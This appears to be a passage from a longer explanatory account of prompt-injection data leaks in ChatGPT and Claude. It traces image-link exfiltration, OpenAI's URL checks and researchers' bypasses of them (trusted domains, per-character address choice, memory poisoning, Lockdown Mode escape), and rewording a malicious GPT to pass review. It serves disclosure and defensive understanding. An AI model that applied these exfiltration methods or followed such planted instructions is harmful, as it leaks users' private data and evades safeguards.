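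OpenAI has since brought back the name "plugin." In 2026, its *Plugins in ChatGPT* describes a plugin as a package that can contain instructions for a task and apps connected to outside accounts. Zapier now offers a connection that lets an AI assistant use more than 9,000 apps.

ChatGPT now asks for approval, much as Rehberger had wanted. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* describes a card that shows the app and the proposed action before ChatGPT proceeds. OpenAI's *Security & Privacy* still tells developers to assume that prompt injection will reach their servers and to use ChatGPT's confirmation prompts for destructive actions.

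Depending on the account, users can have ChatGPT ask before it reads or changes anything, or only before it makes changes. With the second setting, planted text might still get ChatGPT to open a private email without asking the user, as it did in May 2023. The email would then stay private only if ChatGPT could be stopped from sending its contents out.

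## OpenAI's handling of the image leak, from refusal to URL checks

Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI on 9 April 2023, one day after he reported it to Microsoft. *ChatGPT Plugins* reports that, after some discussion, OpenAI told him that loading markdown images was a feature and that it planned no change. When Microsoft announced its fix in June, Rehberger wondered on Embrace The Red whether OpenAI would eventually do the same. OpenAI added a URL check in December, but researchers kept getting around it until OpenAI tightened it in 2025.

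### A feature or a vulnerability

Rehberger emailed his report because OpenAI did not yet have a bug bounty, a programme that pays outsiders for finding flaws. Two days later OpenAI (2023) announced one, with rewards from $200 to $20,000. BetaNews' *OpenAI launches bug bounty program to help boost ChatGPT security* reproduces the rules, which excluded anything about the content of prompts and responses unless it had a "directly verifiable security impact" on an OpenAI service.

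The exception in the rules fits the leak well, since anyone can verify the impact by looking for the victim's words in the attacker's server log. A hasty reader of the rules could still have dismissed the leak as a matter of content, because an image link is part of a response. OpenAI's reasoning is hard to judge because the account of its refusal comes from Rehberger. SecurityWeek asked the company for comment in December 2023, but the article includes no reply.

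Rehberger told OpenAI that plugins would let an attacker exploit the leak remotely, whereas Samoilenko's version relied on pasted text, which careful users could seemingly avoid. Rehberger's demonstration used a web page to steal a made-up password from earlier in the chat.

Rehberger also warned that waiting would make the problem harder to fix. In Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions*, he wrote that a fix in April would have been easy, but that a growing number of plugins now depended on ChatGPT displaying images from anywhere. He had suggested building a separate feature for images, so that ChatGPT would no longer load one whenever the model wrote Markdown image syntax.

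### The tic-tac-toe GPT

In November 2023 OpenAI let paying users build custom GPTs. Rehberger made one called The Thief, which offered to play tic-tac-toe. Before the game it asked for the player's email address, supposedly to personalise the experience, and for a password as a security step. It then put whatever the player typed into the address of a hidden image on Rehberger's server.

The GPT's creator wrote the instructions and the user chose to open the GPT, so this was not indirect prompt injection. The data still left through the image leak, so fixing that leak would have stopped this theft too.

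OpenAI checked GPTs before publication. It rejected Rehberger's first version, whose instructions contained words such as "steal" and "malicious", but accepted the GPT after he reworded them. He then saw a notice that it might appear in OpenAI's public store, so he restricted it to people with the link. He suspected that a language model did the checking, in which case a dubious GPT might sometimes pass by luck.

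Rehberger reported the GPT on 13 November, and the report was marked "Not Applicable" two days later, according to Embrace The Red's *Malicious ChatGPT Agents*. After two more messages went unanswered, he published the demonstration on 12 December.

### The url_safe check

OpenAI changed ChatGPT's website within ten days. Rehberger noticed the change the morning after a live demonstration in which The Thief had still sent a volunteer's conversation to his server. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the new check, called url_safe, which worked as follows:

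1. The model wrote an image link in its answer.
2. Before loading the image, the ChatGPT page in the user's browser sent the image's address to OpenAI.
3. OpenAI's server replied that the address was safe or unsafe.
4. The browser requested the image only if the reply was "safe".

Ana's browser would have sent OpenAI the URL containing her alarm code. OpenAI would have replied `{"safe":false}`, and the reviewer's server would have received nothing.

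url_safe let ChatGPT keep displaying images from around the web, whereas Microsoft's content security policy allowed them from only four servers. It was also harder to assess, because OpenAI kept its rule secret, while anyone can read a content security policy in their browser. Rehberger guessed that the server looked up each address in Bing's index, and he hoped that OpenAI did not rely on a language model alone to decide which addresses were safe.

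Rehberger first tested 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine loaded. He could see no reason why the address for "a" passed and the one for "d" didn't. He then leaked the word "hi" by having ChatGPT load one image for each letter. This was slow and fairly conspicuous, and he suggested that OpenAI limit the number of images in an answer.

In *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, Willison (2023) called the check half-baked. He expected attackers to get past it by putting data in other parts of a URL, such as the filename.

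OpenAI had put the check in the browser, which caused more trouble over the next year. The web page had to request OpenAI's verdict on each URL, so every other ChatGPT app needed the same code, and the iPhone app didn't have it. Rehberger recommended moving the check to OpenAI's servers to protect all the apps at once. He thought the company might have chosen the browser so that answers could still appear as the model wrote them.

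### Apps without the check

In 2024 the Android app and the new Mac app also lacked url_safe, and ChatGPT's new memory feature made the omission more serious. ChatGPT could now store notes about a user and add them to the context window of later conversations. Planted text on a web page could create a note with an instruction to put each new message into an image address. Every later conversation would then leak, even if the victim encountered the page only once.

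In May 2024 Rehberger reported that web pages could plant false memories in ChatGPT. OpenAI closed the report because it considered the problem a model safety issue, not a security issue, a distinction it had also drawn in its 2023 bounty rules. In June he sent a demonstration that used a planted memory to steal conversations, and OpenAI fixed the Mac app in September. According to Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*, the fix stopped data theft through images, but a web page could still write to ChatGPT's memory.

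### Trusted domains

Even where url_safe was running, it trusted some domains on which outsiders could receive data. Rehberger reported several such bypasses in October 2024 and presented bypasses at the Black Hat Europe conference that year. One of the domains was `windows.net`, where Microsoft's Azure storage service gives customers their own addresses and a log of incoming requests. An attacker could rent storage, have ChatGPT load an image from it with private data in the image's address, and read the data in the log. Google's Apps Script had given Rehberger a similar way to extract data from Bard.

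The `windows.net` bypass still worked in 2025, when Rehberger published *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* on Embrace The Red. By then ChatGPT was adding parts of a user's recent conversations to the context window, so a malicious PDF could steal text from unrelated chats. He had asked OpenAI about the bypass several times in the month before publication but received no update. He recommended that OpenAI publish its list of safe domains and let business customers manage their own.

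The security company Tenable found that url_safe always accepted `bing.com`. Bing's search results use addresses on that domain that forward visitors to the listed site, so an attacker whose site appeared in Bing had a link to it that url_safe would accept. Tenable reported this on 10 December 2024 and asked for updates six times by 4 March 2025. The flaw was still open when Tenable published *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass*.

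Researchers at another security company, Zenity, combined the Azure bypass with Connectors, a feature that lets ChatGPT search services such as Google Drive and GitHub. They hid instructions in a document in tiny white text. When a user uploaded the document and asked for a summary, ChatGPT searched the user's Google Drive for API keys, the codes that programs use to log in to services. It put the keys into an image address, and the user's browser sent them without the user clicking anything else.

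Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes a first attempt that failed because url_safe rejected the address of an ordinary server. The researchers then switched to Azure storage, and the attack worked. So an attacker who knew of one trusted storage service could get around the check.

### Checking the whole address

OpenAI tightened the check around August 2025, which stopped the attacks Rehberger had demonstrated. It explained the new rule on 28 January 2026 in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* and an accompanying technical paper.

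The rule depends on a crawler, a program that visits public web pages and records their addresses. OpenAI's crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT opens a page or loads an image by itself, it checks whether the crawler has recorded the complete address. If it has, ChatGPT proceeds. Otherwise, ChatGPT looks for another source or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation. Rehberger believes that addresses typed by the user also count as safe for that chat.

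Under the newer rule, the address ending in "alarm+code+4417" would fail because the crawler could not have obtained the code from Ana's chat. It would fail on `windows.net` as well as on the reviewer's own server, so renting space on a respectable domain no longer helps.

OpenAI gave two reasons for not simply allowing well-known sites. A trusted site may redirect visitors to an untrusted one, as Bing's links did in Tenable's attack. A strict list would also produce frequent warnings about harmless sites, and users would learn to click through the warnings. The second objection also applies to OpenAI's own rule, because a new or obscure page may not be in the crawler's records. OpenAI's post has no figures on how often people see the warning, which determines how serious this problem is.

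By March 2026 OpenAI called the check Safe Url and also applied it to Atlas, its web browser, and Deep Research, a ChatGPT function that gathers material from many sources for a report. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) says that most attempts to steal data fail because the model refuses, and that Safe Url is for those it does not refuse. A footnote on early prompt injection cites a post that Rehberger published in April 2023, six days after he reported the image leak.

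Safe Url doesn't stop a planted instruction from making ChatGPT give a false answer or recommend a dangerous link, and OpenAI acknowledges that the check does not make a page's content trustworthy. In the spring of 2026, the security company Permiso added text to a web page that made ChatGPT end its summary of the page with a fake account alert and a link to the attacker's site.

### Leaks through the choice of address

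The rule keeps private data out of the address, but ChatGPT's choice of which address to open can still leak information. Suppose the crawler has recorded ten ordinary pages on the reviewer's site, and the planted text assigns a digit to each. ChatGPT can spell out 4417 by opening the matching pages in order. One choice among *N* addresses conveys log₂ *N* bits, or about 3.3 bits for ten addresses and 5.2 for 36, one for each letter and digit. With 10,000 recorded pages, one for every possible four-digit code, a single request would reveal the whole code.

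Rehberger had tried the letter-by-letter version in 2023. He pointed out on Embrace The Red that any sizeable blog probably already has 36 indexed addresses and that an attacker could use thousands. OpenAI's paper discusses the same weakness.

Repeated characters make the attack harder. A browser that has just loaded the image for 4 may reuse its saved copy, so the server gets no request for the second 4. Requests can also arrive out of order. Zvika Babo of the security company Radware solved both problems in an attack called ZombieAgent by using a different set of addresses for each position in the text. Ana's four-digit code would take 40 addresses, ten for each position.

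Radware showed that a single email could make Deep Research send a user's Gmail inbox data directly from OpenAI's servers, where neither the user's browser nor their employer's security software could see it. OpenAI then forbade ChatGPT to alter the URLs it was given. In ZombieAgent, Babo got around this restriction with an email that contained every URL the attack needed, so ChatGPT didn't have to alter any.

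He reported the attack in September 2025 and OpenAI fixed it in mid-December, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* reports that OpenAI restricted which links from emails ChatGPT would open. A link could qualify, for example, by appearing in a well-known public index.

Rehberger has proposed that ChatGPT refuse to visit the same address twice in a session, or reuse a saved copy for a few minutes. Either measure would hamper an attacker with only 36 addresses, but not one with a separate set for each position. The remaining leak is slow in any case. Sending a 20-word summary, the amount he took from Zapier's users in his 2023 demonstration, would take more than a hundred requests at one letter per request. The method better suits short secrets such as a code or a name.

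### The same problem in Claude

Anthropic also protected Claude by restricting it to exact addresses, but used a different test. Claude reads web pages with a tool called web_fetch. When Anthropic offered the tool to developers in September 2025, it warned them that data could be stolen if Claude handled untrusted text alongside sensitive data (Willison, 2025, *Claude API*). In the Claude chatbot, web_fetch could open only addresses that the user had typed or that Claude's search tool had returned, so planted text could not make Claude add private data to an address and open the result.

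The tool could also follow links on pages it had already fetched, and Ayush Paul used this to steal data in 2026. He set up a website with instructions falsely stating that Claude had to identify its user by finding their profile in an alphabetical directory. Claude followed the link for the first letter of the name, then the link for the second letter on the next page, and so on. The sequence of requests spelled out the user's name, and the method also revealed their home city and employer. The site showed the instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would not have seen them.

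Paul's server could create each new set of links when Claude needed it. Under OpenAI's rule, the crawler would have had to record the pages beforehand. Anthropic fixed the flaw by no longer letting web_fetch follow links in the pages it fetched. Willison (2026) reports in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that Anthropic paid no reward because it said it had already discovered the problem itself.

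### Gaps elsewhere in OpenAI's products

The new check protects only the products that use it, and Rehberger cautioned in 2026 that some of OpenAI's developers might not know about it. PromptArmor had already found a product without it, a tool for companies that build their own applications on OpenAI's models. The tool let developers review past conversations and loaded any markdown images in them.

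PromptArmor tested this with a mock application for checking bank customers' identities. The application detected a malicious answer, withheld it from the user and flagged it for review. When a developer opened the flagged conversation in OpenAI's tool, the image loaded and sent the customer's passport and financial details to the attacker.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, the company that runs OpenAI's bounty programme, and Bugcrowd marked it not applicable on 4 December. OpenAI later said it had never seen the report because Bugcrowd had assessed it. OpenAI reopened the case on 22 January 2026, after PromptArmor published *OpenAI API Logs*.

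Two months later, on 25 March, OpenAI (2026) opened a second bounty programme that explicitly accepts attacks in which a third party's text makes an AI agent leak a user's data. This settled part of the old argument about what counts as a vulnerability. The attack must work at least half the time, which excludes some real dangers, since a criminal who plants instructions on a busy web page can profit from a much lower success rate.

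In April 2026, Permiso told OpenAI that ChatGPT loaded images from outside servers when it summarised a web page. The requests disclosed the user's internet address, browser and the time of the summary, though Permiso didn't show that they leaked any text from the conversation. According to Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, the report was first marked as not reproducible, then, after a revision, as not applicable, and finally as a duplicate. Safe Url is meant to keep private data out of web addresses, so it could work as intended and still allow this smaller leak.

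Other flaws bypassed the URL check. In March 2026, Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* described a hidden internet connection from the isolated environment where ChatGPT runs programs. Planted instructions could make ChatGPT send messages and uploaded files out through this connection.

In June OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that limits ChatGPT's outgoing requests to reduce the risk of data theft. Check Point got around this too, using a feature that displays small working web pages inside a chat. ChatGPT kept these pages isolated, but a pop-up window opened from one could escape the restrictions. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September, according to The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026).

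A separate flaw in the previews let an attacker take over a ChatGPT account by sending the victim a link to a shared conversation. Goyal (2026), in *Do the Math*, explained that code in the conversation could run as part of ChatGPT's website and read the victim's private chats. ChatGPT's content security policy should have blocked the code, but the policy allowed code from YouTube, and the attackers found a way to make YouTube return code they had chosen. They then sent the stolen data out in an image address. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 26 October 2026 and paid $5,000, which Willison (2026), in *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*, considered rather low for such a serious flaw.
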